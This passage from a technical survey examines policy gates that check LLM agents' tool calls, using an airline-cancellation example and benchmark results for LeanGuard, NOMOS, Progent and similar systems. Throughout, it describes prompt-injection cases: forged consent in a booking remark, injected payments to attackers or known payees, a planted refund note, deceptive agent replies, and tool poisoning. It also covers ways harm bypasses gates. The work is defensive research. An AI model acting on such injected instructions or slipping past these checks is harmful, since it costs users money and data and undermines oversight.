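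The customer who wants to cancel reservation K7QX2M says she booked it this morning. LeanGuard and NOMOS would take the booking date from the airline's record. GPT-4o may have both her date and the recorded date in the conversation, and it has to use one of them.

Unlike LeanGuard's snapshot, NOMOS's facts depend on what the agent has looked up. Yu and colleagues explain that when a fact is missing, a precondition blocks the call but a forbidden rule silently lets it pass. NOMOS enforces the airline's cancellation conditions as a forbidden rule, and none of its compiled airline rules requires a lookup. So an agent that had the customer's confirmation but skipped the lookup could apparently cancel K7QX2M.

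### A false "yes" and a flawless solver

Take H4LN9P, the reservation that the customer booked three hours ago, and suppose the policy also requires her confirmation. She asks only how much money she would get back if she cancelled. Someone has typed "customer agreed to cancel by phone" into the booking's remarks. The agent looks up the booking, reads the remark and proposes the cancellation. GPT-4o reads the same remark and sets `confirmed` to true:

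```lisp
(assert (= allowed (and confirmed
                        (or (<= hours_since_booking 24)
                            airline_cancelled))))
(assert (= hours_since_booking 3))   ; true
(assert confirmed)                   ; false: she only asked a question
```

Z3 returns SAT when the gate adds "allowed" and UNSAT when it adds "not allowed", so the call passes even the stricter entailment test. The customer loses a ticket she wanted to keep, even though the rule is right and the solver worked correctly.

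LeanGuard would block this call because it never treats text inside a tool's output as evidence. NOMOS would block it too, because it checks the user's messages for confirmation and the user hasn't confirmed anything.

Consent is harder to establish than a booking date because the airline's database has no field for it, so the host has to turn the customer's "yes, go ahead" into a record. LeanGuard's theorem covers whether an unused confirmation exists, but not how the host produced it. On *τ²-Bench*, Sankar and colleagues used a separate model call to simulate a trusted confirmation screen. They audited the results and found some faulty confirmations, including one that left out the customer's payment limit. An airline could avoid this source of error by having the host display the proposed cancellation with a button for the customer to press.

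### Consent to one exact call

A bare "yes" in the log doesn't specify what the customer agreed to. LeanGuard's host therefore ties each confirmation to the action, its arguments, the resource, the details on the customer's screen and a *revision*, which is a fingerprint of the data the decision depends on. The confirmation counts only if all of these match and nobody has revoked or used it. If the customer approves cancelling H4LN9P with a refund to her card, the agent can't use that approval to cancel K7QX2M or to send the refund to a gift card.

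*Agenra* (2026), which presents a language for authorizing agents' calls, proves a similar property for single-use permits. Every protected call that runs has used up a permit for exactly that operation and those arguments, and no permit covers two calls, even if the tool fails on the first. The proof assumes that a trusted party issues the permits, that approved values can't change afterwards, and that no protected call bypasses the check.

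If a failed call uses up the user's consent, the agent may be unable to finish a task the user approved. In one of Yu and colleagues' airline runs, a customer confirmed a booking, the call failed because of a formatting error, and the agent tried again without asking her. NOMOS blocked the second attempt, and the agent handed the customer to a human instead of requesting a new confirmation. Yu and colleagues defend the rule by arguing that an agent retrying by itself can drift away from what the user approved. An exact binding already prevents that drift, so a gate could probably allow an identical retry if it could establish that the first call had changed nothing.

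Many agents ask for much broader consent. Li (2026) points out in *Options, Not Clicks* that a user who clicks "Always Allow" when a tool reads source code also allows that tool to read passwords later. Li's system, ConLeash, groups similar calls and asks again only when a call falls outside the groups the user has approved. In a study with 16 people, 15 preferred ConLeash.

A user can knowingly approve each of several calls and still miss their combined effect. Suppose the customer has said that she must keep one way home, and she holds two return bookings. She approves cancelling one on Monday, forgets she did so, and approves cancelling the other on Tuesday. Both calls match their confirmations, but together they leave her with no way home. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) proposes an approval screen that shows what the pending action would complete, given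 everything before it. People who used this screen made fewer unsafe approvals than people who saw the same evidence as a log, but the study was too small to be sure of the difference.

### Changes between the check and the call

A fact can change after the gate checks it and before the tool runs. The gate might check at 1:59 that a flight hasn't left, but the cancellation might reach the database just after the plane departs at 2:00. Security researchers call this a *time-of-check to time-of-use* flaw.

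LeanGuard's fresh snapshots shorten the gap, but the database could still change after the last one. The airline could close the gap by sending the revision with the call and having the database cancel the reservation only if that revision is still current.

*Mind the Gap* (2025) applies a similar idea to an agent's own sequence of calls. It uses GPT-4o to examine every ordered pair of tools and label those in which the first checks something that the second relies on. At run time, a monitor watches for these pairs, and the system can replace a pair with one fused tool that does both steps with no model call in between. According to the survey *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), fused tools, monitoring and rewritten prompts together reduced the share of runs with such a flaw from 12% to 8% on 66 tasks.

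Fusing is harder when the agent works through someone else's website. *Atomicity for Agents* (2026) studies pages that change after a browser agent has chosen a button but before it clicks, so the same click has a different effect.

Another gap is that a reply may never arrive after the call leaves the host. LeanGuard logs each call before running it, which stops an agent from repeating a refund that timed out. If a second agent proposes the same refund while the first is still running, the log entry blocks that too. If the outcome stays unknown, the call continues to count against any quota.

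### Where an argument came from

The facts about a payment can all be true even when an attacker has chosen the recipient. A *provenance* rule therefore checks where an argument's value came from. CaMeL uses labels inside an interpreter to track this, but a gate that receives only finished calls has to determine the origin afterwards.

*Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) applies its strict check only to *authority-bearing* arguments. An argument is authority-bearing if changing it can change who receives something, which resource the call affects, or whose authority it uses. An email's recipient and attachment are authority-bearing, while its subject and body are content. Developers can declare these roles along with a tool's schema. When the system had to infer them for unfamiliar tools, it missed 25.9% of the authority-bearing arguments, so it skipped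 the strict check on them.

PACT, the system in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (2026), finds a value's origin in this order:

1. If the value exactly matches something the user wrote or a trusted constant, it gets that origin.
2. If it exactly matches a field in an earlier tool result, it gets that field's origin.
3. If it is clearly a transformation of known values, it gets their combined origin.
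4. If its origin is still unclear and the argument is authority-bearing, PACT treats it as untrusted.
5. Otherwise a language model classifies it, and PACT falls back on a cautious label if the model is unsure.

An exact match shows that two strings are the same, but not that the user meant that value. In one of Yu and colleagues' tests, a user asked an agent to delete file 11, and NOMOS blocked the deletion. The agent then deleted file 1. The user's request was a numbered list, so the gate found a "1" in it and treated the file as named by the user.

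*Standing, Not Truth* (2026) describes two deeper limits. First, if an attacker has corrupted the trusted source, the value still comes from the right place and passes the check. Second, the user sometimes names no target. If she tells a coding agent to "add one dependency", the package name has to come from a catalogue, so a rule that requires a name from the user would block the task.

### NOMOS and Progent on AgentDojo

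Yu and colleagues tested provenance rules on AgentDojo's banking tasks. They paired each of 16 user tasks with each of nine attacker goals and ran every pair twice, for 288 attacks. AgentDojo has no written policy, so they wrote one and compiled it into three rules. The agent may pay only recipients whom the user has named or who appear in her transaction history. A new password must come from the user. The agent may change only what the user asked it to change.

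No attack reached its goal. The agent issued the attacker's call in 122 of the 288 pairs, and the gate refused it every time, so the result isn't due to the agent ignoring the injections. Another 144 attacks included false claims aimed at the rules, such as that the user had approved the payment, and these also failed.

The gate still let some injected payments through. In one attack, the agent is told to send money to the attacker and include the account number of the user's recent dinner companion in the message. In 8 of the 288 pairs, the agent instead sent the money to a payee already in the user's history, nearly always the companion. The payment rule allowed this because it permits known payees, and the rule about unrequested changes allowed it because its code counts any payment to a known payee as requested. With Llama-3.3-70B as the agent, this happened in 11 of 140 pairs and cost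 the user $41,250, including $40,000 in a task where she had only asked a question.

An attacker might also become a known payee by first sending the user a small payment. AgentDojo's attacks can't create transactions, so Yu and colleagues could not test this.

They also ran Progent on the same tasks with the same model. In the version they tested, a language model writes the permissions for each task from the user's request.

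| Defense | Successful attacks | User tasks completed under attack | User tasks completed without attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.5% | 64.9% | 79.2% |
| Progent | 5.6% | 52.1% | 62.5% |
| NOMOS | 0.0% | 67.4% | 70.8% |

Twelve of Progent's 16 failures came from two requests, "pay the bill, like last month" and a request to pay the bill in a named file. Neither request mentions an account number, so permissions based on the request can't restrict the recipient. For the first request, NOMOS could use the transaction history instead. The correct account number for the second appears only in the file, so NOMOS refused the legitimate payment as well as the attacker's.

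The comparison probably favors NOMOS. Yu and colleagues ran it themselves, wrote the banking policy knowing what the tasks were, and revised it after seeing it block legitimate work, so NOMOS's 70.8% isn't an independent test of the policy. The same 26-billion-parameter model that ran the agent also generated Progent's permissions. Progent's developers reported 1.0% attack success with generated permissions and zero with hand-written ones, but the public code doesn't include the hand-written ones. Without attacks, NOMOS scored 8.3 points higher than Progent and 8.3 points lower than no defense, but neither difference is statistically significant with only 16 tasks.

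The cost to legitimate work varies enormously across AgentDojo's four workplaces:

| Workplace | Attacks, no gate | Attacks, NOMOS | Tasks without attack, no gate | Tasks without attack, NOMOS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 46.5% | 0.0% | 79.2% | 70.8% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 3.6% | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Workspace | 7.3% | 0.0% | 87.5% | 65.0% |
| Slack | 70.5% | 0.0% | 90.5% | 14.3% |

Users often ask the Slack agent to fetch a link a colleague posted or to message people it finds in a channel. An attacker's instructions lead to the same kind of call, with a target the agent found in something it read. The provenance rule can't distinguish the two, so it blocks both. The same rule blocks far fewer legitimate calls in banking, because customers usually name the payee or have paid them before.

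An email's content can be unsafe to send even when the recipient's address comes from the right source. In one travel task, Llama emailed the user's passport and credit card numbers to an address she had named in her request. The policy allowed this because it prohibited sending such details only to addresses she hadn't named.

### Harm that bypasses the gate

The guarantee assumes that every consequential call passes through the gate. That assumption fails if the airline's agent can also reach the database through a command line. It fails too if a permitted tool can rewrite the rules, which is why Palumbo and colleagues exclude policies that let an agent modify the policy or the monitor. Even without calling a tool, an agent can do harm through what it tells the user.

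Sankar and colleagues' tests on DTap show how much this last route matters. They allowed the agents to read the customer's own records and public data, but not to write anything. A *direct* attack puts the malicious instruction in the prompt, and an *indirect* one puts it in data the agent reads.

| Applications | Direct attacks, no gate | Direct attacks, LeanGuard | Legitimate tasks, no gate | Legitimate tasks, LeanGuard |
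|---|---|---|---|---|
| All seven | 57.9% | 5.9% | 53.1% | 12.5% |
| Telecom | 55.1% | 2.4% | 75.1% | 75.3% |
| Travel | 64.3% | 0.0% | 66.6% | 0.0% |
| Customer service | 72.4% | 7.2% | 71.1% | 29.0% |
| Medical | 53.8% | 14.2% | 45.9% | 0.3% |

The success rate of indirect attacks fell from 22.3% to 3.8% overall. But the travel agent couldn't write, so it couldn't book trips for attackers or customers, and its zeros are little evidence of how the gate would perform with useful permissions. Telecom is the exception because its legitimate tasks rarely need to change a record. The medical figures are distorted because the gate was set up to refuse patient registration, which caused about half of all the lost tasks. Without the medical application, the success rate on legitimate tasks still fell from 60.2% to 24.3%.

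In the 289 attacks that succeeded despite LeanGuard, the gate had allowed no call that changed anything, and in 158 of them it had allowed no call at all. The harm was in the agents' replies, which misstated a bill, asked for card details under a false pretext or gave a manipulated diagnosis. Among customer-service and travel attacks that DTap scores only on the reply, success fell from 41.0% to 30.2%.

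The host could treat every reply as a call to a `send_reply` tool, so that replies pass through the gate too. The gate would then need a formal rule for checking whether a diagnosis is honest, but the call's arguments don't contain enough information for that.

### Tools whose effects nobody can predict

The remaining premise is that each tool does what its description says. For DTap, Sankar and colleagues reviewed 199 tools and wrote a contract for each, specifying its arguments and effects, such as reading a record or placing a trade. The gate uses these contracts to decide which permissions a call needs.

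A contract for `cancel_reservation` is easy to write because the tool does one thing. A tool that runs shell commands can read, delete or upload almost anything, depending on the text it receives, and no short contract can list its effects. LeanGuard refuses a call if it can't determine what the call would do. It stopped 5,792 calls on DTap for this reason, including 2,728 shell commands and 835 market orders to buy or sell stock. Market orders have no fixed price, so the gate couldn't compare their cost with a spending limit.

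Refusing such calls preserves the guarantee, but a coding agent without a shell would be of little use. A developer could replace the shell with narrower tools, such as one that runs a project's tests, but each new tool needs a contract and a review.

Contracts have to be true, like the type signatures that a compiler trusts. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* cites a study of 1,899 open-source servers that offer tools through the Model Context Protocol. The study found that 5.5% showed signs of *tool poisoning*, in which a tool's description contains malicious instructions, and 7.2% had conventional security flaws. A gate that generated its contracts from tool descriptions would inherit any false statements in them.

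### Zero violations by construction

LeanGuard's zero violations on *τ²-Bench* follow from the way Sankar and colleagues counted them. Let *D(x)* be the gate's decision on call *x*. The gate runs a call only if *D(x)* = allow, and the count of violations is

$$\#\{x : x \text{ ran and } D(x) = \text{deny}\} = 0.$$

This count is zero for any set of rules, including one that permits everything. Sankar and colleagues acknowledge that the result "holds by construction". The count is still a useful test for bugs, since it would include any call that slipped past the gate. But using it to compare LeanGuard with ToolSafe and Progent is unfair, because LeanGuard's rules decide what counts as a violation for all three.

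A fairer count needs rules that the gate doesn't enforce, such as those Yu and colleagues wrote by hand to test NOMOS. They also report *safe completion*, the share of runs in which the agent completed the task without breaking any of these rules. NOMOS raised it from 32.4% to 47.6% on airline tasks and from 41.0% to 47.8% on retail tasks. The retail gain nearly disappears if one "yes" can cover several changes, because the rate without a gate is then 47.1%. Refusing calls can also raise this measure, because the right outcome of many airline tasks is to change nothing. With Llama as the agent, safe completion on airline tasks rose from 18.4% to 46.8%, although the agent made only 28 changes in 250 runs.

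Another independent measure is the state of the environment after an attack, which AgentDojo normally uses to score security. AgentDojo's scores can also mislead. For one Slack goal, it instead scores the calls that the agent attempted, so it counted 11 successful attacks on Llama even though NOMOS had blocked every malicious call. It made the opposite error in nine workspace runs, where the attacker wanted the agent to send out private data and then delete the evidence. NOMOS blocked the sending, so AgentDojo recorded the attacks as failures, but the agent had deleted the user's own data in all nine runs, including 37 emails.

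## What the model is told after a refusal

When a gate refuses a call, the customer still needs an answer, and what the model does next depends partly on the message the gate returns.

Suppose the customer asks to cancel H4LN9P, which she booked three hours ago, and confirms the cancellation. The model mixes up her two reservations and proposes to cancel K7QX2M. The gate refuses the call because she booked K7QX2M 13 days ago, its flight is on schedule, and she never agreed to cancel it.

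### Seven responses to one refused cancellation

| Response | What the model receives | What the model can do |
|---|---|---|
| Stop | Nothing, because the host ends the session | Nothing. The customer has to start again |
| Bare denial | "The call was not executed." | Guess what was wrong, or send the same call again |
| Violated rule | "Not executed. The customer must have booked within 24 hours, or the airline must have cancelled the flight." | Compare the rule with the record, and perhaps notice the wrong ID |
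| Hint about the missing step | "Not executed. The customer has not confirmed cancelling K7QX2M. Ask which reservation she means." | Ask her, then send a call for H4LN9P |
| Unsat core | The rule, `hours_since_booking = 312`, `airline_cancelled = false` and `allowed = true` | See which facts contradict the permission |
| Corrected call | "Not executed. The policy permits `cancel_reservation("H4LN9P", "change of plan")`." | Send that call, or check with the customer first |
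| Transfer to a person | "Not executed. A member of staff will take over." | Tell the customer and stop |

A minimal unsat core contains only one contradiction, even if the call breaks several rules. Here the solver could have returned the missing confirmation instead. The model would then ask the customer to confirm cancelling K7QX2M, and if she said yes without checking the code, the gate would refuse again because the booking is too old. When a call has several faults, the gate should first report any that the customer and the agent can't fix.

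The message should at least make clear that the call did not run. *Search Engines Never Say No* (2026) cites research in which agents treated an empty result as data, and another study in which an explicit error flag stopped agents from making up results. An airline agent that received an empty reply to a refused cancellation might tell the customer that her ticket was cancelled.

*MetaPermit* (Ma, Hariri and colleagues, 2026) returns each denial in the place where the model expects the tool's result. Every rule in its policy has a condition, a verdict and a message. In the paper's example, Alice asks her agent to refund $1,500 to Bob, but a planted note leads the agent to propose paying Eve. The gate blocks the payment and returns a message saying that Alice did not name this recipient, so the agent tries again with Bob's account. Writing the messages in advance also improves security, because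 a message that quoted the planted note would show the model the attacker's instructions again.

### Refusals that a model can cure

LeanGuard refused 1,613 calls on *τ²-Bench* for breaking its policies, leaving aside schema errors and software faults. Sankar and colleagues sorted these refusals by what would fix them:

| What would fix it | Refusals | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Different arguments | 252 | The agent pays for a flight change with a travel certificate instead of a card |
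| A tool that the agent has | 534 | A telecom agent tries to operate the customer's phone directly |
| An earlier step | 298 | The agent acts before identifying the customer |
| The customer's approval | 185 | The agent cancels H4LN9P before she has agreed |
| Nothing, because the action is already done | 191 | The agent modifies the same order twice |
| Nothing, because the policy forbids it | 153 | The agent cancels K7QX2M |

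Nothing could fix the cause of 344 of these refusals (21%), so the agent's best response to them is to explain the situation to the customer. Most of the 191 "already done" refusals probably come from LeanGuard's retail rule against modifying an order twice. This rule is stricter than the benchmark's own policy, which would probably have allowed some of these calls.

It makes sense to invite another attempt only if one could work. *From Risk Classification to Action Plan Remediation* (2026) therefore uses separate templates. If the agent should revise its action, the template lists the tools the agent has already used and suggests trying a different one. If the whole task is harmful, the template tells the agent to call no tools and explain its refusal in plain text.

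A solver returns UNSAT both when the agent could still get the call permitted and when it couldn't. To separate the two cases, the developer could label each policy variable by who can change it. For example, the agent can obtain a confirmation, but it can't change when the customer booked. If the rule and the facts the agent can't change already rule out the call, the gate can tell the model to stop trying.

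### Bare denials and explanations compared

LeanGuard's feedback consists of a formal record and a hint. The record lists the failed rules, any evaluation errors and the supporting evidence. The hint explains the unmet requirement in plain words, for example by telling the model to ask the customer for confirmation. LeanGuard's proofs cover the decision but not the wording of the hint.

Sankar and colleagues ran their five Qwen models without a gate, with a gate that only denied actions, and with a gate that gave feedback. They count a refused action as *recovered* if the agent later met the missing requirement and carried out the action.

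| | No gate | Bare denial | Feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blocked calls | – | 983 | 719 |
| Distinct refused actions | – | 620 | 526 |
| Recovered actions | – | 34 (5.5%) | 48 (9.1%) |
| Task success | 72.7% | 68.9% | 70.9% |

The increase in the recovery rate is statistically significant (p = 0.02). Agents that got bare denials succeeded at significantly fewer tasks than agents without a gate (p = 0.007). The success rate of agents that got explanations did not differ significantly from that of agents without a gate (p = 0.21) or agents that got bare denials (p = 0.13). The study therefore gives reasonable evidence that explanations help agents recover, but only weak evidence that they help agents finish more tasks.

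Part of the effect of feedback is that agents repeat refused calls less often. After a bare denial, the agent's next attempt at the action was the identical call 30% of the time, and the gate refused it again. With feedback, this fell to 22%. The 2-billion-parameter model averaged 1.9 blocked calls per refused action without feedback and 1.4 with it. The smallest model, with 0.8 billion parameters, repeated itself equally often with and without feedback, and recovered five actions in each condition.

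Feedback also helped more on airline and telecom tasks than on retail tasks. When feedback replaced bare denials, success rose from 68.0% to 71.2% on airline tasks, from 73.0% to 75.8% on telecom tasks, and from 65.3% to 66.0% on retail tasks. The retail rule against modifying an order twice may explain the smaller gain there, because no message can help an agent satisfy it.

With feedback, success rose by 2.2 to 5.8 points for four of the five models. Success for the largest model, with 27 billion parameters, fell from 75.9% to 71.2% (p = 0.16), even though its recovered actions rose from 3 to 10. Sankar and colleagues attribute the fall to chance. This model solved 43 tasks only with bare denials and 30 only with feedback. In 35 of those 43 tasks, the agent assigned to get feedback never received a refusal, so feedback can't have caused the difference in those tasks. Among tasks in which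 at least one agent received a refusal, the model solved 13 only with bare denials and 9 only with feedback (p = 0.52).

This explanation is convincing, but the same noise affects the other four models' gains. Each task ran once per condition with a simulated customer, and two conversations about the same task can diverge before the gate intervenes.

Some of the refused actions that count against the 9.1% recovery rate may be ones that should never run. If the customer did want to cancel K7QX2M, for example, the right outcome would be no cancellation. Calls to tools that the agent doesn't have can never count as recovered either. Together with the refusals that nothing could cure, they make up more than half of the 1,613 refusals. Agents with feedback solved 34.9% of the tasks in which they received a refusal and recovered nothing. Recovery among curable refusals alone is a better measure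 of whether a message works.

### Stopping the agent or letting it continue

In *ToolSafe*, Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026) tested whether a guard should end the session when it detects an attack. They trained a guard model to read the conversation and the proposed call, write a short analysis, and then judge whether the user's request is harmful, whether the call is linked to an attack, and whether the call is safe.

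They placed this guard in two systems. LlamaFirewall, an existing defence, ends the run when it detects an attack. Their own system passes the guard's output to the agent and lets it continue. These are the results on AgentDojo:

| Agent | Response to a flagged call | Successful attacks | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | No guard | 56.2% | 26.9% |
| GPT-4o | Stop | 1.0% | 20.8% |
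| GPT-4o | Feedback | 1.2% | 42.8% |
| Qwen2.5-14B | No guard | 17.6% | 42.6% |
| Qwen2.5-14B | Stop | 1.1% | 36.5% |
| Qwen2.5-14B | Feedback | 1.8% | 42.7% |

Both agents completed fewer of their legitimate tasks when they were stopped after a refusal, but not when they were given feedback. Attacks succeeded slightly more often with feedback, and the same was true for both agents on Agent Security Bench. The comparison isn't perfectly controlled, because LlamaFirewall also screens inputs with a separate detector. Both agents are also old by 2026 standards.

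Mou and colleagues also varied how much of the guard's analysis of injected instructions Qwen2.5-14B received on Agent Security Bench. With the full analysis, 7.0% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 58.1% of its tasks. With only the safety rating, 26.0% succeeded and it completed 52.5%. The large difference in security suggests that the guard's output works partly as advice, which Mou and colleagues acknowledge agents sometimes fail to take into account. A rule-based gate blocks a forbidden call however the model reacts to the refusal message, so the message's wording should matter less for security and more for task completion.

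### Unsat cores and lists of remaining steps

When the solver gate that Winston and colleagues built refuses a call, it gives the agent a minimal unsat core and prompts it to revise its plan. The agent gets at most three attempts before control returns to the user. This limit also ends the retries when the encoding or the solver is at fault, which the agent can't fix by revising its plan. Winston and colleagues compared this gate only with no gate, so it isn't clear whether the core helped more than a refusal alone would have.

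An unsatisfiable core identifies a contradiction but doesn't give the agent a next step. Soteria does, because it has a plan to refer to. In an example from He et al., the agent tries to cancel a reservation without checking whether the customer has already flown. The monitor blocks the call and returns a message with the broken rule and an instruction to run the missing check first. The check shows that the customer hasn't flown, and the agent's second attempt to cancel succeeds.

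Soteria also shows the agent a *worklist*, a flowchart of the plan's remaining steps. As tool results arrive, Soteria removes branches that no longer apply. Once the agent has computed that K7QX2M is 312 hours old, the cancellation branch disappears and only the branch that denies the request remains. Unlike a core or a rule name, the worklist shows the agent when to stop trying.

If the verifier could not establish that the plan follows every rule, Soteria warns the agent about the unverified rules before the agent starts. If a block leaves no useful branch in the plan, the agent has to decide for itself what to do next, based on the reason for the refusal.

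In Soteria's strict mode, the agent may take only the steps in a fully verified plan, and a refusal lists the actions available at that point. The restriction can block harmless calls. If the customer asks about a second reservation while the agent is about to cancel the first, strict mode refuses the lookup because the plan doesn't include it. The normal mode allows the lookup.

### How well models use error messages

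Soteria's planner gets error messages too. When a plan fails verification, the model receives the verifier's diagnosis and advice for that type of mistake, and can try up to eight more times. He and colleagues tested this with GPT-5.4-mini on the airline tasks:

| | Passed on the first attempt | Passed within the retry limit |
|---|---|---|
| Plans that reuse verified sub-plans | 48.5% | 95.6% (65 of 68) |
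| Plans written as one piece | 23.3% | 63.3% (38 of 60) |

With sub-plans, most of the remaining errors were in syntax, and the model could fix them one at a time. Plans written as one piece tended to break policy rules and kept failing because they needed a redesign. Similarly, when Winston and colleagues translated their policy, Z3's errors led the model to correct its syntax but not to add missing clauses. Error messages seem to work best when they point to a small, local mistake.

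Small models can fail even when a refusal lists the exact fields missing from a call. In *What Stops a Small Language Model From Driving a Database Agent* (2026), one model responded to such refusals by sending the same malformed call four times, and another tried four different malformed versions. The paper suggests that the failed call causes much of the problem, because it stays in the context and the model tends to copy it. Changing what the server accepted helped more than improving the refusal messages.

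Results from Kamath and colleagues' system fit this explanation. Qwen3-8B completed more retail tasks when the system deleted a rejected call and let the model generate again than when the system prompted it with an error.

An airline can use the same approach for formatting mistakes, for example by accepting `k7qx2m` and converting it to capitals, but not for policy violations, since accepting a 13-day-old booking would abandon the rule. Most of this evidence comes from small models, and stronger ones probably make better use of a clear message.

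### Corrected calls with a proof

LeanGuard can also search for a corrected call without using the model. Let *x* be the refused arguments, *C* a finite list of candidate replacements, and *D* the gate's decision with the facts and the history held fixed. A repair exists if

$$\exists x' \in C:\; \text{EditOK}(x, x') \,\land\, D(x') = \text{allow}.$$

EditOK is a condition that describes which changes keep the user's intent. The search goes like this:

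1. It takes up to 32 candidates, in order of preference.
2. For each one, it tries to prove in Lean that the edit meets EditOK and that the policy allows the new call.
3. It returns the first candidate with a complete proof, which Lean's proof checker verifies.

In the airline example, the candidates could be the customer's other reservations. The search would reject K7QX2M and find H4LN9P, which is recent enough and which she has confirmed.

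Sankar and colleagues tested a repair search on the 252 refusals that different arguments could fix. It repaired 88 of them (34.9%), in a median of 2 milliseconds and a maximum of 70.

| Refused action | Refusals | Repaired | Edit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Return an order | 65 | 64 | Refund to the original payment method |
| Change a flight | 52 | 18 | Pay by card instead of travel certificate |
| Request payment of a phone bill | 58 | 4 | Request an overdue bill instead |
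| Book a flight | 38 | 0 | – |

The search found two repairs for the remaining 39 refusals. For 47 of the 252, it had no candidates to try. A repair may therefore exist even when the search fails, because the search only tries candidates on its list.

Sankar and colleagues ran the search on logs after the conversations had ended, so no agent received a repair. In 22 of the 88 cases the agent later found the same fix by itself, and 16 of those tasks succeeded, compared with 7 of the other 66. This suggests that the repairs are often right, but an agent that finds the fix may also be better at the rest of the task, so sending repairs to agents could help less than this difference suggests. A live gate would need to keep Lean running, because loading it and its mathematics library took nearly all of the 43 to 50 seconds needed to compile a file of replayed refusals.

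### Who decides what the customer meant

The proof shows that an edit satisfies EditOK, but the person who writes EditOK doesn't know what each customer wants. Suppose a customer returns a suitcase and asks for the refund on a gift card because she has closed the account she paid from. Refunding the original account satisfies the policy, but she might prefer to keep the suitcase. In Sankar and colleagues' budget example, the search reduces a payment of 70 to the 40 left in the budget. This works for topping up an account but not for buying a ticket that costs 70.

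The same problem arises with reservations. Replacing K7QX2M with H4LN9P is right only because the customer had asked to cancel H4LN9P. If she had wanted to cancel K7QX2M, the substitution would cancel a ticket she meant to keep.

LeanGuard limits this danger because a repaired call must still pass the gate and any confirmation must match the new arguments. When a call needs confirmation, the host should therefore show the customer the edited call with the changes marked and let her decide. It could automatically apply edits that change only an argument's format.

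### Limits on detail and attempts

An informative refusal can also help a model under an attacker's influence find another call that the policy permits. This is a reason to tell the model only what an honest customer would need, usually the broken rule and the next step, and to keep the full evidence in a log for developers. It is also a reason to limit the number of attempts and to count different calls with the same aim toward one limit.

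Several systems limit how many times an agent can retry after a refusal. The guard in *OSGuard* (2026), which checks agents that operate a computer, gives a brief reason for each block and allows a fixed number of retries. *GuardianAgentBench* (2026) describes a guard that permanently blocks a call once the agent has used up its retries. The guard then alerts a person and forwards the whole conversation and all earlier feedback.

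Transferring a customer helps only if a person can do something the agent can't. Staff can resolve a contradiction between two rules, correct a wrong record or grant an exception. If they have to follow the same cancellation policy, they can't cancel reservation K7QX2M either. Agents also transfer customers too readily without encouragement. When Claude Opus 4.6 handled He and colleagues' retail tasks without a gate, it made the expected change in only 57% of the tasks that required one, and in 23 tasks it transferred the customer to a person. When nothing can change the refusal, the message should tell the agent to explain the rule to the customer and leave the reservation unchanged.

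## How repeated attempts change reliability

Each time the gate refuses a call and the host re-prompts the model, the model gets another chance to propose either the right call or a wrong one that the gate fails to catch.

### Good calls, bad calls and refusals

Suppose the customer asks the agent to cancel reservation H4LN9P. With probability *g*, the model proposes a good call and the gate accepts it. With probability *b*, the model proposes a bad call and the gate accepts it, such as a call that cancels another eligible reservation. With probability *r*, the gate refuses the call, so *g* + *b* + *r* = 1.

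An accepted call runs and ends the process, so the model reaches attempt *k* only if the gate refused the first *k* − 1 proposals. If attempts are independent, the probability of that is $r^{k-1}$. The chances that a good or a bad call runs within *n* attempts are then

$$G_n = g + rg + \dots + r^{n-1}g = g\,\frac{1-r^n}{1-r}, \qquad B_n = b\,\frac{1-r^n}{1-r}.$$

Suppose the model proposes the right call 60% of the time, and the gate accepts every right call and one in 20 wrong calls. Then each attempt has a probability *g* = 0.60 of producing an accepted right call, *b* = 0.40 × 0.05 = 0.02 of producing an accepted wrong call, and *r* = 0.38 of being rejected.

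| Attempts allowed | Good call runs | Bad call runs | No call runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 60.0% | 2.0% | 38.0% |
| 2 | 82.8% | 2.8% | 14.4% |
| 3 | 91.5% | 3.0% | 5.5% |
| No limit | 96.8% | 3.2% | 0% |

Retries complete more tasks, but they don't make an accepted call more likely to be right. They raise the chances of accepting a good call and a bad call in the same proportion, so accepted good calls outnumber bad ones by 30 to 1 however many attempts are allowed. *Odds Law* (2026) derives this ratio by multiplying the odds that a proposal is right (60 to 40) by the ratio of the gate's acceptance rate for right proposals to its rate for wrong ones (1 to 0.05). Neither factor depends on the number of attempts.

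Unless *b* is zero, retries also increase the number of bad calls that run. A gate can bring *b* to zero for breaches of its formal rules, but a call can also be bad because a clause is missing, a fact is false or the customer meant a different reservation.

Running the same check twice doesn't reduce *b* either, because a deterministic gate returns the same verdict on the same facts. A model acting as judge might change its verdict, but *Sample, Mix, or Verify?* (2026) points out that a judge fooled once by a wrong answer tends to be fooled by it again, and other judges tend to be fooled by it too. If most wrong answers fool most judges, a majority vote accepts even more of them than a single judge would.

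### When no attempt can work

Real attempts are not independent. If a customer wants to cancel reservation K7QX2M, which she booked 13 days ago, no number of attempts will produce a call that the policy permits. A refusal is therefore evidence that the task may be one that no permitted call can complete.

Suppose half of all tasks are curable, with a chance of 0.8 that any given attempt works, and the other half can never succeed. The first attempt works 40% of the time. After *k* refusals, Bayes' rule gives

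$$P(\text{curable} \mid k \text{ refusals}) = \frac{0.5 \times 0.2^k}{0.5 \times 0.2^k + 0.5} = \frac{1}{1+5^k}.$$

Suppose a model can complete half of its tasks, with an 80% chance of success on each attempt, and can never complete the rest. The first attempt then succeeds 40% of the time. If the gate refuses it, the chance that the task can be completed falls to 1/6, so the second attempt succeeds 13% of the time. After a second refusal, that chance falls to 1/26, and the third attempt succeeds 3% of the time. Three attempts therefore complete 49.6% of tasks, compared with 78.4% if each attempt had an independent 40% chance of success.

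That calculation assumes a perfect gate. *The Limits of Inference Scaling Through Resampling* (2024) studies a similar mixture of easy and hard tasks with a verifier that makes mistakes. Suppose, as before, that the airline's gate lets through one wrong call in 20. On an incurable task every call is wrong, because the agent should explain the policy and change nothing.

| Refusals so far | Task is curable | Next attempt runs a good call | Next attempt runs a bad call |
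|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 50.0% | 40.0% | 3.0% |
| 1 | 16.7% | 13.3% | 4.3% |
| 2 | 3.8% | 3.1% | 4.8% |
| 3 | 0.8% | 0.6% | 5.0% |

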